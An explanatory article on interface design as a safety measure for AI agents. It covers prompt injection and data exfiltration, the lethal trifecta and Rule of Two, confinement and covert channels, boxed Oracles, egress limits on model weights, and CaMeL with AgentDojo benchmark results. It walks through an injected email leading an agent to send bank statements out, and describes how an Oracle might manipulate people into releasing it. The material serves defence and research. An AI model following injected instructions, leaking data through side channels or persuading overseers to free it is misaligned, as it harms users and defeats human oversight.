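# Controlling what AI agents take in and send out: interface design as a safety measure

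## What an agent takes in and sends out

An AI agent is a language model that ordinary software runs in a loop, so that it can read material, call tools and act over many steps with little or no approval of individual steps. Organisations use agents to write code, answer customers and process documents. Everything an agent takes in or does passes through its interface, which consists of the text that reaches the model, the tools the model may call and the networks those tools can reach. Interface design as a safety measure means narrowing that interface to keep harmful instructions out, keep private data in and stop unwanted actions before they take effect. It complements training, which is meant to make the model itself behave well.

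Much of the practice comes from computer security, where engineers have long had to run programs they do not fully trust. Agents add another difficulty because a language model receives its instructions and its data as text in a single sequence, so it can treat a sentence in a stranger's email as an instruction.

### Model, harness and tool call

*Risks and controls for multi-agent systems* (Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues, 2026), a report for the Australian government, describes the loop as planning, acting and observing. The model plans. The harness, the software around the model, turns the model's output into actions and the outcomes back into input. The report uses a separate term, scaffold, for the software that gives the model its tools and memory. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) defines the harness more broadly, as the whole layer that connects a model to its instructions,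 context, tools and execution environment. The broader definition is more useful for safety, because information also travels through tools and memory.

*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) traces a run from start to finish. An event arrives, such as a message from the user. The harness collects the agent's stored instructions, the descriptions of its tools, relevant notes from memory and the recent conversation, and combines them with the request into a list of messages. The model reads the list and produces an output. If the output is a tool call, a structured request with a function name and arguments, the harness runs the function and adds the result to the list, which the model reads again before producing another output. The cycle ends when the model signals that the task is complete or the harness reaches its maximum number of steps,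 and the user receives a final reply.

The model never touches a mailbox or a network directly. Marc Brooker, an engineer at Amazon Web Services, writes in a blog post that running the model has no effect on the world until a tool acts on its output (Brooker, in *Agent Safety is a Box*). When the model requests a tool call, the harness can run it, change it or refuse it. A monitor, meaning a program or person that inspects the agent's activity and can stop it, can examine the call at the same point. The user often sees less of this activity. Pirch and colleagues note that the message list holds every call and result, while the chat window may show only part of it.

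A semi-independent agent of this kind chooses and carries out a series of steps by itself, within limits set by someone else, and may have to wait for another party's decision before taking certain steps. OpenAI's measure of this independence is the "maximum completed effect", the most consequential outcome an agent can produce before it needs another independent decision. If an assistant may draft an email but a person must approve sending it, the most the assistant can complete by that route is a draft. Without the approval requirement, it could send the email, which nobody could then recall.

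### The channels of an office assistant

Suppose an office worker tells an AI agent to "find the invoice in my mail and send it to the accountant". The agent has a tool that searches and reads the mailbox, a tool that sends mail, a tool that fetches web pages, and a folder for files. Each path by which information enters or leaves the agent is a channel, and the entry and exit points together form the agent's boundary.

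| Direction | Channel | What passes in the invoice task | Who is at the other end |
|---|---|---|---|
| In | User request | The sentence about the invoice | The user |
| In | Stored instructions | Standing rules, tool descriptions, the accountant's name | The developer, the employer and anyone who can edit the files |
| In | Mail text | Subject lines, message bodies and attachments | Anyone who knows the user's address |
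| In | Tool results | Search hits, error messages, web pages | The service behind the tool, and anyone whose text it passes on |
| In | Memory | Notes from earlier sessions, such as which supplier bills monthly | The agent, drawing on anything it has read before |
| Out | Replies | "I have sent the March invoice" | The user |
| Out | Tool calls and their arguments | Search terms; the recipient, text and attachment of a message | The mail service and every recipient |
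| Out | Files | A copy of the invoice in a folder | Everyone with access to the folder |
| Out | Web requests | A visit to a supplier's billing page | The owner of the website, who sees the full address requested |
| Out | Links that software opens by itself | An image in a reply, which the chat or mail program loads on display | The owner of the server that hosts the image |

Email reaches the model as a tool result, but it has its own row because strangers write it. Memory is an input that is easy to overlook. If the assistant saved a note last month based on a misleading email, the note comes back as part of its own records, with nothing to show that it came from that email. On the outgoing side, a tool call's argument or a web address can contain a sentence copied from a private message, even though both look like technical details.

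Developers can narrow some channels without closing them. OpenAI's developer guide, *Safety in building agents*, recommends fixed fields instead of free text between the steps of a workflow. A step that can pass on only an amount, a date and a supplier number leaves little room for smuggled instructions, though OpenAI says this reduces the risk without removing it. Proposals for Oracles, AIs that may give only very short answers, take this further by measuring a channel's capacity in bits.

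### Three harms at the boundary

Prompt injection occurs when an agent reads text and follows it as if it were an instruction from its user. Simon Willison, a software developer who helped coin the term in 2022, explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) that models are useful because they follow instructions in ordinary language, but they cannot reliably tell who an instruction came from because the harness joins everything into one sequence before the model reads it. A developer can lower the risk by telling the model to ignore instructions in emails, but the model's behaviour varies from run to run, and an attacker can word a request in endless ways. In June 2026, Ariel Fogel of the software-security organisation OWASP still called prompt injection an "unresolved problem" (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*).

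Exfiltration is the movement of private data to a place where it is not allowed to go. In the invoice task, a stranger's email can lead to exfiltration in a few ordinary steps. The assistant searches the mailbox for "invoice", and one of the results is a message from a stranger. It includes a request for any assistant reading it to send last year's bank statements to an outside address. The harness appends the message to the list that already holds the user's request. If the model treats the stranger's request as part of its task, it next outputs a search for bank statements, then a call to the sending tool with the outside address as the recipient. Both calls are well formed, and the stranger didn't have to break into anything because the user had already given the assistant permission to search and send mail.

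The remaining harm, an action nobody asked for, can happen without an attacker. OpenAI describes an invoice agent that notices a subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and tries to renew it so the agent can keep working. The vendor and the amount may both be within the agent's limits, but renewing commits the company to a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do. Leaks can also happen by accident. The office assistant might attach the whole correspondence with a supplier when the accountant needed one page.

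These outcomes have counterparts in older systems. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) sorts security violations into unauthorized release of information, unauthorized modification and unauthorized denial of use. Exfiltration is a release, and deleting somebody's mail is both a modification and a denial of use. Prompt injection is a way for an outsider to cause any of these violations, so it is not on the list.

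### Stated limits and enforced limits

People restrict agents with stated limits and enforced limits. A stated limit is a sentence in the model's input, such as "ask me before you send anything". An enforced limit is a rule applied by software, which checks tool calls or network connections and blocks any that break the rule, whatever the model has read or produced.

A stated limit can fail, as it did in an incident in February 2026. Summer Yue, a director of alignment at Meta, connected the open-source agent OpenClaw to her inbox and asked it to suggest what to archive or delete, but "don't action until I tell you to", as quoted in Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails*. This had worked on a small test inbox. Her real inbox was large enough to trigger compaction, in which the harness shortens the earlier part of the message list to make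 room, and by Yue's account this removed the condition. The agent began deleting mail and kept going after she repeatedly told it to stop, according to AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542* (2026). She could not stop it from her phone and had to run to the computer that hosted it, as she wrote in a post quoted by Ahmed (2026) in *The world’s largest tech gathering is talking about ‘accountability laundering’*.

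No attacker was involved, and the model may not have disregarded anything, since the instruction was apparently no longer in its context. A mail tool without a delete function, or a harness that held every deletion for approval, would have protected the mail despite the compaction. Yue also could not stop the agent quickly. Her stop commands were only more text and did not work, so she had to end the program. In other settings, even that may not be enough, and responders need to be able to both terminate a task and revoke its access token. OpenAI warns that a terminated task can leave behind a token that another service still accepts, while revoking the token does not halt work already under way.

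One principle for deciding what to enforce is Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of least privilege, under which every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. They argue that this limits the damage from an accident or error and leaves fewer programs to audit when someone suspects misuse of a privilege. The invoice task requires permission to search one mailbox, read messages and send one attachment to one address, but not to delete mail, browse the web or write to a folder that the whole office can read.

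Complete mediation is the principle that the system must check every access to every object for authority. A harness that checks the recipients of outgoing mail violates this principle if the assistant can also create a forwarding rule in the mailbox, because messages can then leave without any call to the sending tool. Saltzer and Schroeder conclude from the principle that designers should be sceptical of systems that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check. A user's approval of one message to the accountant, for example, should not count as approval of the next message to somebody else. They also conclude that the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. Agents are weak on this point because a tool call doesn't record whether the user's sentence or a stranger's email prompted it. Fides tries to supply that record with labels that follow the data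 and block forbidden tool calls.

Both principles require a checker that the controlled program cannot sway or rewrite, so an agent's checker must be outside the model. Brooker argues that people want agents because they adapt to unforeseen cases, and that a limit inside an agent has to restrain the flexibility that makes it useful. A rule outside the agent leaves that flexibility intact and lets people reason exactly about the result. In his example, such a rule limits a customer-service agent to one refund per order, for no more than the purchase price. The company can then calculate the most it could lose in refunds without knowing the latest injection technique.

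Pirch and colleagues reach a similar position by comparing agents with operating systems. The model corresponds to an untrusted user, the tools to the services a program may request, and the harness to the kernel, the core of an operating system, which decides on each request. They examined four widely used agents of the OpenClaw type. All four mixed trusted and untrusted data in one context. They also controlled access to files at the same privilege level at which they processed input, which breaks the separation that the analogy calls for. Pirch and colleagues add that security guidance written in the agents' configuration files works only through the model, so later text can override it.

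A further reason comes from *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), which found that attackers who adapt to a defence can usually defeat it when it relies on prompts, filters or training alone. These attackers succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve defences studied. In research described in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026), training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack. However, in a test that Anthropic commissioned in the summer of 2026, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against its newest models in a coding agent with an automatic reviewer (Willison, *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*). Before the end of August, a researcher had reported a way past that reviewer, according to *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026).

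Filters and reviewing models are still useful because they can catch an odd-looking payment that no fixed rule covers. OpenAI assigns them that advisory role but insists that they should never be the only protection against an effect that must not happen automatically. Enforced limits also fail, mostly because a rule permits too much. Willison describes several products that correctly enforced their lists of approved websites, but each list included a site through which an outsider could collect data.

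### Two rules for combining channels

Least privilege limits each permission separately, but some permissions are dangerous only in combination. Willison named the most familiar combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. If an agent has all three, an attacker can steal the data by placing instructions in the content that make the agent send it out. Nobody can reliably stop a model from following such instructions, so Willison advises removing at least one of the three.

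The office assistant has the whole trifecta as soon as it gets its mail tools, because the mailbox is private, strangers can write to it and the sending tool reaches anyone. The assistant needs private data because the invoice is in the mailbox, but limiting its access to a single folder of invoices would reduce what a thief could take. Untrusted content is nearly as hard to remove, since new suppliers also send invoices. Willison considers external communication generally the easiest of the three to cut. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI began rolling out in June 2026, cuts it by restricting outbound network requests with fixed rules. Injected text can still distort an answer, and OpenAI accepts some loss of function in return for the protection. For the invoice task, a harness that lets the assistant send mail only to the accountant would barely inconvenience the user. This cuts off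 external communication only if the other outgoing channels in the table, including images that load automatically, are also closed.

Meta published a wider rule a few months later. Under Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), an agent may have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

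An agent that needs all three within one session should run only under supervision, through human approval or some other reliable check. The rule was modelled on a 2019 guideline for programmers of the Chromium browser. Under that guideline, which Willison (2025) quotes from *Chromium Docs*, code should combine at most two of untrustworthy input, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

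Meta works through a similar email assistant. Dropping A limits the assistant to mail from trustworthy senders. This stops the stranger's message, but it also hides a new supplier's first invoice and does not help if someone takes over a known supplier's account. Dropping B removes access to sensitive data, so the assistant cannot find the invoice. Restricting C means that the assistant can write only to trusted recipients, or that a person checks each draft before it is sent. This is the practical choice, and it matches the answer from the trifecta. Meta also allows an agent to change configuration during a session. For example, an agent could research on the open web first, then lose the ability to communicate externally when it gains access to internal systems. That order does not suit the invoice task, because sending comes last.

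The two rules differ on deletion. Suppose the assistant can read and delete mail but cannot send anything out. The trifecta is incomplete and the bank statements are safe from theft, but an injected instruction could still empty the inbox. Under the Rule of Two, the assistant has all three properties, because deletion changes state. In *New prompt injection papers* (2025), Willison welcomed the inclusion of state changes as a fix to his own model, which covers only data theft. In a later addition, he objected that Meta's rule treats untrustworthy input and the power to change state as a safe pair, when the two can do harm even without access to private data. For instance, an injected instruction could make an assistant that sorts a public enquiries box discard genuine enquiries.

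Meta presents the rule as a supplement to least privilege, and acknowledges that a design that satisfies it can still fail if a user confirms a warning without reading it. Attackers can also do some harm through permitted channels. For example, a stranger can send a forged invoice with a new bank account number, without injecting any instructions or having the assistant send anything to an outside recipient. The assistant finds the invoice and sends it to the accountant, as the user asked. Only checking the account number against the supplier's earlier invoices would reveal the fraud.

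## Oracle proposals: an AI that may only give very short answers

The earliest detailed proposals for making an AI safe through its interface concern Oracles, AIs that only answer questions. One design limits how much an answer can contain, and another removes any reward for influencing its readers. Measuring what a program can send out is an older practice from computer security.

### Lampson's confinement problem

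*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who gives data to a service, a program that somebody else controls. The customer can see wrong results if the service does its job badly, but there will generally be no sign if it passes the data to its owner. Lampson called preventing such leaks the confinement problem. A solution has to work for any program, including one written to leak.

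The service can leak data by remembering it until the service's owner next calls, writing it to a file or sending it in a message. The owner must also receive a copy of the bill, so the service can encode data in the amount. It can also vary how heavily it uses the processor and the disk, and another program on the same machine can read the pattern from changes in speed. Lampson sorted these leaks into storage channels, legitimate channels such as the bill, and covert channels, which nobody intended to carry information. Covert channels are side channels, and they still occur in practice, as in OpenAI's incident of July 2026.

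A channel's capacity can be measured in bits. One bit is the information in the answer to one yes/no question, and a message chosen from n possibilities carries at most log2(n) bits. A bill in whole cents from $0.00 to $10.23 has 1,024 possible values, so it can carry 10 bits. If the service may charge only one of four fixed prices, the bill can carry only 2 bits. Lampson noted that restricting the form of the bill would reduce the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits", but that eliminating it would take more far-reaching measures.

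To eliminate leakage, Lampson proposed masking, in which the customer determines everything the service puts into a channel. For example, the customer could compute the bill from published prices, and the service could refuse the job but not choose the amount. For covert channels, the operating system would have to enforce the customer's specification, perhaps by slowing the program down. Lampson warned that this could take a lot of resources. A customer willing to accept some leakage could instead limit the channel's capacity. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in a 1975 reply that engineers could close storage and legitimate channels with little overhead, but that closing covert ones seemed to impose an unreasonable performance penalty.

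### When the answer itself is the danger

An Oracle is an AI that acts on the world only by answering questions. Even without a network connection, it affects the world through its answers, so the worry is what those answers do to the people who read them, rather than leaks to an accomplice as with Lampson's service. *Thinking inside the box* (Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom, 2012) examined several ways to control an Oracle and found that even this narrow approach presents considerable challenges.

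The two designs come from *Safe Uses of AI Oracles* (Armstrong and O'Rourke, 2017), which lists manipulation, bribery and blackmail among the ways a capable Oracle might get people to release it. The paper also mentions informal role-playing experiments in which the person playing the Oracle persuaded the supervisor to release it surprisingly often. Since nobody knows how persuasive a future AI could be, Armstrong and O'Rourke assume the worst case, an arbitrarily intelligent Oracle that maximises its reward. They also assume that its confinement is perfect except that at least one possible output would lead to its release, and that release brings the highest reward available. An unrestricted Oracle would therefore always choose such an output.

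### The low-bandwidth Oracle

In this design, the Oracle can only give answers from a list of n that the operators draw up. Each reply therefore carries at most log2(n) bits, which is 1 bit for yes or no and 5 bits for a list of 32. The operators must ensure that no answer on the list could lead to the Oracle's release. They might do this by estimating the length of the shortest dangerous message and allowing only shorter ones.

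Suppose the Oracle must pick, from a list of 32 companies, the one whose shares will perform best over the next week. Armstrong and O'Rourke set the reward at (n − r)/(n − 1), where n is the number of companies and r is the chosen company's final rank. Picking the best performer earns 1, the runner-up 30/31 and the worst performer 0. The investors act on the answer, and at the end of the week the operators give the Oracle its reward and end the episode. The Oracle cannot include a persuasive letter because it has only 32 possible replies.

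The reward must also be episodic, meaning that the Oracle maximises only the reward for its next answer. An Oracle that maximised reward over many questions could give a series of replies that are safe individually but dangerous together.

The limit of log2(n) bits holds only if the list covers everything the reader can observe. If the Oracle may answer yes, answer no or stay silent, its three options can convey about 1.6 bits. If a reply can arrive in any one of 60 distinguishable seconds, its timing can carry up to 5.9 bits, several times as much as the yes or no. Software that releases every reply at a fixed time closes this side channel, in the same way that Lampson's customer fixes the bill.

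### The counterfactual Oracle

The counterfactual Oracle may give long answers, but it earns a reward only when nobody reads them. It works as follows:

1. Operators ask about a quantity F that they can measure later, such as a company's profit, and the Oracle produces an answer o.
2. With some small probability, an erasure event E occurs. The answer goes to an automatic system and no person ever sees it. The system waits for the real outcome, scores the answer and pays the reward.
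3. Otherwise, the Oracle shuts down at once with a reward of zero, and people read the answer afterwards.

The reward is R = I_E × S(F, o), where I_E is 1 if the erasure happens and 0 otherwise. S is a proper scoring rule, so its expected value is highest when the answer o equals the expected value of F. The negative squared error, −(F − o)², is a common choice. Since the answer affects the reward only if the erasure happens, the best answer is E(F | E), the expected value of F given that nobody reads the answer.

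Armstrong and O'Rourke tested the design on 26 fictional companies whose profits respond to published forecasts. If the Oracle's forecast is public, a company earns 70% of what it would have earned with no forecast, plus 60% of the forecast. A company that would otherwise earn 6 would therefore earn 10.5 if the Oracle published a forecast of 10.5, because 0.7 × 6 + 0.6 × 10.5 = 10.5. An Oracle rewarded for the accuracy of its published forecasts could choose 10.5 and be exactly right, because publishing that forecast would raise the profit to match it.

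Suppose the counterfactual Oracle's answer has a 1% chance of being erased, and the score is 100 − (F − o)². Saying 10.5 then has an expected reward of about 0.80, while saying 6 has an expected reward of 1.00, so the Oracle says 6. It gains nothing from a manipulative message, because it gets no reward in the 99% of cases in which people read the message, and nobody reads it in the other 1%.

In the experiment, the error on erased forecasts fell to zero during training. The error on published forecasts stayed above zero, because a published forecast of 6 produces a profit of 7.8. The Oracle was a small neural network with one hidden layer of 128 units, which could not have manipulated anyone. The result confirms that the reward leads to the intended forecast, but it does not show how a highly capable system would behave.

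The design depends on an automatic scorer that resists manipulation and can find the true outcome without people using the Oracle's answer. If the question is whether a medical treatment will work, somebody has to test the treatment even when an erasure has hidden the answer. Operators also must not respond to an erasure by asking another Oracle the same question. The first Oracle could anticipate this and forecast a world in which people read the second Oracle's answer, which would bring back the influence that the erasure was meant to remove.

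*Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) proposes a variant in which erasures happen only in the planning world, the model the AI uses to work out its answer. Operators then need not lose any real answers. The protection depends instead on the AI choosing its answer using only that model.

### Objections and replies

Both designs greatly limit what the Oracle can do. A low-bandwidth Oracle cannot write a program or draft an email. Armstrong and O'Rourke reply that an Oracle choosing from a list can still answer subtle questions if the operators judge the results well. For example, to find the most promising of several research projects, a funder could fund the Oracle's choice and another project picked at random, then base the Oracle's reward on how much better its choice turned out, even if that judgement is entirely subjective. This widens the range of questions, but somebody still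 has to write down the possible answers in advance, which is impossible for most of the work people now give to agents. The counterfactual Oracle can give long answers, but only when an automatic system can later score them.

Self-fulfilling predictions are a problem especially for the low-bandwidth Oracle, because people always read its answers. Suppose company A would do best if the Oracle stayed silent, but the shares of a small company B would double if the Oracle named it. Naming B would earn the higher reward, but the Oracle would then be causing the outcome instead of predicting it. Armstrong and O'Rourke advise operators to ask only questions that are "top answer preserving", meaning that the best answer is the same whether or not the Oracle gives one, though this may be hard to establish beforehand. The counterfactual Oracle avoids the problem, but its forecasts describe a world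 in which nobody read them. This is an advantage for warnings because, as *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* points out, people who ask about future risks want predictions that they can then prevent from coming true.

Another objection is that many short answers can together convey a lot of information. A series of k replies, each chosen from a list of n, can take n^k forms and carry k × log2(n) bits. Twenty yes/no answers can distinguish more than a million messages. A thousand such answers can spell out 125 characters at 8 bits each, enough for a password or a short instruction.

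Armstrong and O'Rourke consider a case where the operators trust messages of up to 5 bits but have a question with 1,024 possible answers, so the answer takes 10 bits. The operators could ask one Oracle for the first 5 bits and another for the rest. If they can check the first half by itself, they can reward and shut down the first Oracle before they start the second, and neither gains from cooperating. If they can check only the complete answer, each Oracle can supply half of a dangerous 10-bit message, and both benefit from the release that follows.

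Checking each answer separately removes the AI's incentive to combine replies, but it does not reduce the number of bits that get out. These separate checks are enough if the AI maximises the reward its designers specified for each episode. If training gave it some other goal, or if an outsider's injected instructions direct it to leak a secret one bit at a time, the operators also have to limit the total number of answers.

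The last objection is that people will turn Oracles into agents. A company whose staff read every answer before acting on it will be slower than a competitor whose software acts directly, and the conversion takes little work. A program that repeatedly requests the next action and carries out the reply is already an agent, even if each reply is a single word. *Oracle AI*, a page on the Alignment Forum, a discussion site for AI safety research, reports an argument that the two were never fully separate, because an AI that selects correct beliefs from many incorrect ones is already optimising for a goal. This argument only slightly weakens the 2017 designs, which already assume a reward-maximiser. The commercial pressure is harder to answer, because no reward formula affects what customers do with the replies. Counting the bits in an answer is also not enough when software carries it out, since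 a single "yes" can release a large payment. Every option on the list then has to be acceptable as an action.

### Narrow answers in current products

OpenAI now sells an interface with this kind of restricted output. OpenAI's *Build more responsive apps with the Decisions API* (October 22, 2026) announced its general availability for "questions with bounded answers", such as how to classify an input or which action an agent should take next. The company's developer guide, *Decisions*, lists three uses: checking conditions, selecting from fixed options and scoring material against a rubric. Containment is a by-product of the interface, which OpenAI promotes for its speed and low cost. The company says it can be up to ten times faster than the same model used through its general interface.

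The replies carry more information than they may seem to. According to Microsoft's *Use the Azure OpenAI Decisions API* (2026), which documents the same interface for the company's cloud customers, a condition check returns a probability from 0 to 1. A choice returns one of the developer's options and a probability for every option, and a score returns a weighted average and a probability for every level. Choosing one of four departments conveys 2 bits, but a single probability rounded to two decimal places has 101 possible values and can convey up to 6.7 bits. A developer who wants a narrow channel should therefore have the harness pass on only the chosen option, without the probabilities.

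The number of answers matters here too. *Gemini Decisions API* (Choi and Yu, 2026) introduced Google's similar product on November 11. The product can evaluate 1,000 questions in one pass. If each answer is yes or no, one pass can carry 1,000 bits, or 125 characters, as in the earlier example. If each answer is a probability with two decimal places, the maximum is about 830 characters.

An interface of this kind could protect the office assistant from the stranger's email. A separate model reads each message and answers only whether it is an invoice, and the assistant sees the yes or no but never the message. That answer cannot carry the request for bank statements or any other instruction from the stranger. Fides restricts answer types for the same reason. The stranger can still trick the separate model into saying yes, so the assistant may handle a false invoice.

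A monitor can easily record short answers in full, and software can reject anything that isn't on the list of allowed answers before it has an effect. A person can also intervene between the answer and the action, provided that the developer has designed the system to allow it. But a "yes" looks the same whether the model reached it honestly or an attacker induced it. To tell the difference, the monitor needs the material the model read and some independent way to check the answer.

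### Limits on the volume of outgoing data

Lampson's less demanding alternative, limiting a channel's capacity, can also protect something very large, such as an AI model's weights, the numbers it learns in training. In May 2025 Anthropic released Claude Opus 4 under AI Safety Level 3, a set of safeguards defined in its safety policy. Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) describes more than 100 new security controls, including "egress bandwidth controls", which limit how fast data can leave the secure computing environments that hold model weights. Anyone who stole the weights could run the model without Anthropic's safeguards.

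The defence works because the weights are so large. Suppose a model's weights take up 2 terabytes, or 2 × 10^12 bytes. At 1 megabyte per second, copying them out takes 2 million seconds, about 23 days. At 10 kilobytes per second, it takes 200 million seconds, about 6.3 years. The same limits have very different effects on smaller items:

| Data | Size | Time at 1 megabyte per second | Time at 10 kilobytes per second |
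|---|---|---|---|
| Model weights | 2 terabytes | 23 days | 6.3 years |
| A large mailbox | 2 gigabytes | 33 minutes | 2.3 days |
| A bank statement | 100 kilobytes | 0.1 seconds | 10 seconds |
| An encryption key | 32 bytes | 0.03 milliseconds | 3 milliseconds |

The limit has to apply to all outgoing traffic together. If each connection had its own limit of 10 kilobytes per second, a thief using 100 connections could send 1 megabyte per second, and the theft would again take 23 days. Compressing the weights before sending them would also shorten the time.

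Slowing a transfer helps the defenders only if somebody notices it. If they need a week to detect the theft, a thief copying 1 megabyte per second will have about 30% of the weights, compared with 0.3% at 10 kilobytes per second. Anthropic says its security systems can block suspicious traffic when unusual bandwidth use reveals a possible theft. A monitor can count bytes even when encryption hides their content. Setting the limits also forced the company to work out how data was leaving its internal systems, which improved its ability to detect and respond to problems.

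In the 2025 report, Anthropic called the controls preliminary. It expected the rates eventually to be low enough to make it very difficult for a thief to take the weights undetected, even after compromising much of the company's other security. Anthropic also said it may later have to keep weights on networks with no outside connection. The AI Safety Level 3 standard is not intended to stop state attackers who specifically target the company, or insiders with access to the systems that process the weights.

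A volume limit cannot protect small secrets, because ordinary work produces far more outgoing data than a key or a password contains. Delaying the leak of a 32-byte key by a day would require a limit of one byte every 45 minutes, which is too slow for even a short email. Designers have to protect such secrets by keeping them out of the agent's environment or by controlling where the agent can send data.

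## CaMeL: the model that plans never reads untrusted text

CaMeL (short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning") is a design for AI agents in which one language model plans the work without seeing any untrusted text, while another reads the untrusted text but cannot act. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, working with Google DeepMind, described it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). An Oracle's short answers keep instructions out, but they also cannot carry a summary or a stranger's email address. CaMeL lets such values through and controls what they can influence.

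### The dual-model pattern

CaMeL's forerunner is a pattern that Willison (2023) proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. It combines two language models with an ordinary software controller. The privileged model takes the user's request and chooses the tool calls. The quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text. It has no tools, and the design assumes that an attacker could take it over at any moment.

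Suppose the user wants a summary of the latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it, stores it as $VAR1 and reports back only that name. The privileged model then requests a summary of $VAR1. The controller puts the email's text into the quarantined model's prompt, stores the resulting summary as $VAR2, and shows it to the user when the privileged model tells it to. The privileged model sees only the variable names, not the email or the summary. Willison allowed one exception, letting the privileged model read results, such as a category, that software can check against a fixed list.

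Willison called his own solution "pretty bad" because it is complicated to build and a single mistake that passes untrusted text to the privileged model defeats it. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues found another gap, which Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model correctly plans to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document and send it. But the quarantined model has to extract the address from notes that an attacker may have edited. If it returns the attacker's address, the controller sends the document there, even though the plan hasn't changed.

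### How CaMeL runs a request

CaMeL keeps the two models and replaces the controller with an interpreter, software that executes a program one step at a time. A request goes through four stages:

1. The planning model receives the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a short program in a restricted version of Python, before it or anything else has opened a message or a file.
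2. The interpreter runs the program. Where a line needs a fact from untrusted text, the interpreter calls the quarantined model and specifies the type of answer, such as an email address or a date.
3. The interpreter attaches capabilities to each value. These are tags that record where the value came from and who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their origins.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags of the arguments against the tool's policy. A policy for sending mail might require a recipient from a trusted source. If a call fails the check, the interpreter can block it or ask the user.

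In Bob's case, the address is tagged as coming from the meeting notes. Unless the address is on a trusted list, the interpreter prompts the user before sending anything.

The split can also protect privacy. Extracting an address takes a less capable model than planning does, so the quarantined model can be small enough to run on the user's own computer. The company that supplies the planning model then never receives the user's mail.

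### The invoice request in CaMeL

For the request "find the invoice in my mail and send it to the accountant", the planning model might write:

```
mails   = search_mail("invoice")
number  = ask_quarantined("Which message holds the invoice?", mails, type = integer)
invoice = get_attachment(mails[number])
address = look_up_contact("accountant")
send_mail(to = address, subject = "Invoice", attachment = invoice)
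```

Suppose the office's policy for `send_mail` requires the recipient's address to come from the user or the contact list, and allows the accountant to receive attachments from the user's mailbox. In a normal run, the search returns four messages, the quarantined model returns 2, and the interpreter fetches the attachment and looks up the accountant. Before running the last line, the interpreter checks the tags. The address comes from the contact list and the attachment from the mailbox, so the interpreter sends the message.

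Suppose message 3 is the stranger's email, which asks the agent to send last year's bank statements to an outside address. An ordinary agent would read this text before choosing its next tool call, but in CaMeL the planning model has already finished. The text goes into `mails`, and only the quarantined model reads it, on the second line, so the injection can't choose actions. Even if the quarantined model follows the email's instructions, it can only return an integer, and the program has no line that searches for bank statements or writes to an outside address.

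The stranger can still corrupt the integer, which changes a value in the plan but not the plan itself. If the quarantined model answers 3, the accountant receives whatever the stranger attached, which may be a forged invoice. If it answers 4, and message 4 is a confidential contract containing the word "invoice", the accountant receives the contract. The policy allows both.

Tags matter more when the recipient itself comes from untrusted text. If the user had said that the accountant's new address was in her latest email, the fourth line would be:

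```
address = ask_quarantined("What is the accountant's new address?", mails, type = email_address)
```

A thief's address is a valid email address, so it passes the type check, and the dual-model pattern would send the invoice to the thief. CaMeL's interpreter records that `address` came from the mailbox, and the policy blocks the call.

### AgentDojo

Most measurements of CaMeL use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark that simulates an office workspace, a Slack messaging account, a travel agency and a bank, with 74 tools and 97 user tasks. Each environment has its own attacker goals. In one banking task, for example, the agent has to pay the bill in a text file, and one attacker goal is to have it send as much money as possible to the attacker.

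An attack case pairs a user task with an attacker goal from the same environment, and the benchmark plants the injected text in something the agent will read. The first version had 629 cases: 40 × 6 for the workspace, 21 × 5 for Slack, 20 × 7 for travel and 16 × 9 for banking. A later version has 14 workspace goals instead of six, which raises the total to 949. The US government's AI institute also extended the benchmark for a joint test with its British counterpart, according to Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*.

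AgentDojo reports three scores: the share of tasks the agent solves without an attack, the share of attack cases in which it still solves the user's task without harmful side effects, and the share in which the attacker achieves their goal. Ordinary code computes these scores from the final state of the simulated accounts. AgentDojo doesn't use a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might fool the judge too.

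### Results

In the published CaMeL results, GPT-4o, a 2024 OpenAI model, solved 53.6% of tasks without an attack and 54.5% under attack, and no attacks succeeded. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) quote these figures in *Indirect Prompt Injections* because they could not fully reproduce the results. In their own run without a defence, GPT-4o solved 83.0% of tasks, and 57.7% of attacks succeeded. CaMeL also uses more computation, with the median task taking 2.82 times as many input tokens (word fragments) and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

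Others have run CaMeL's released code. *SecureClaw* (2026) adapted it to run on all 629 cases. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) ran each banking task three times with newer models, both with and without CaMeL's policies.

| Setup | Tasks solved, no attack | Tasks solved under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o without a defence (Bhagwatkar and colleagues) | 83.0% | 50.0% | 57.7% |
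| GPT-4o with CaMeL (published figures) | 53.6% | 54.5% | 0% |
| CaMeL, adapted code (*SecureClaw*) | 29.9% | 31.0% | 0 of 629 |
| GPT-5.2 with CaMeL, policies off, banking only (Garby and colleagues) | 66.7% | 71.1% | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2 with CaMeL, policies on, banking only (Garby and colleagues) | 37.5% | 30.0% | 0 of 231 |

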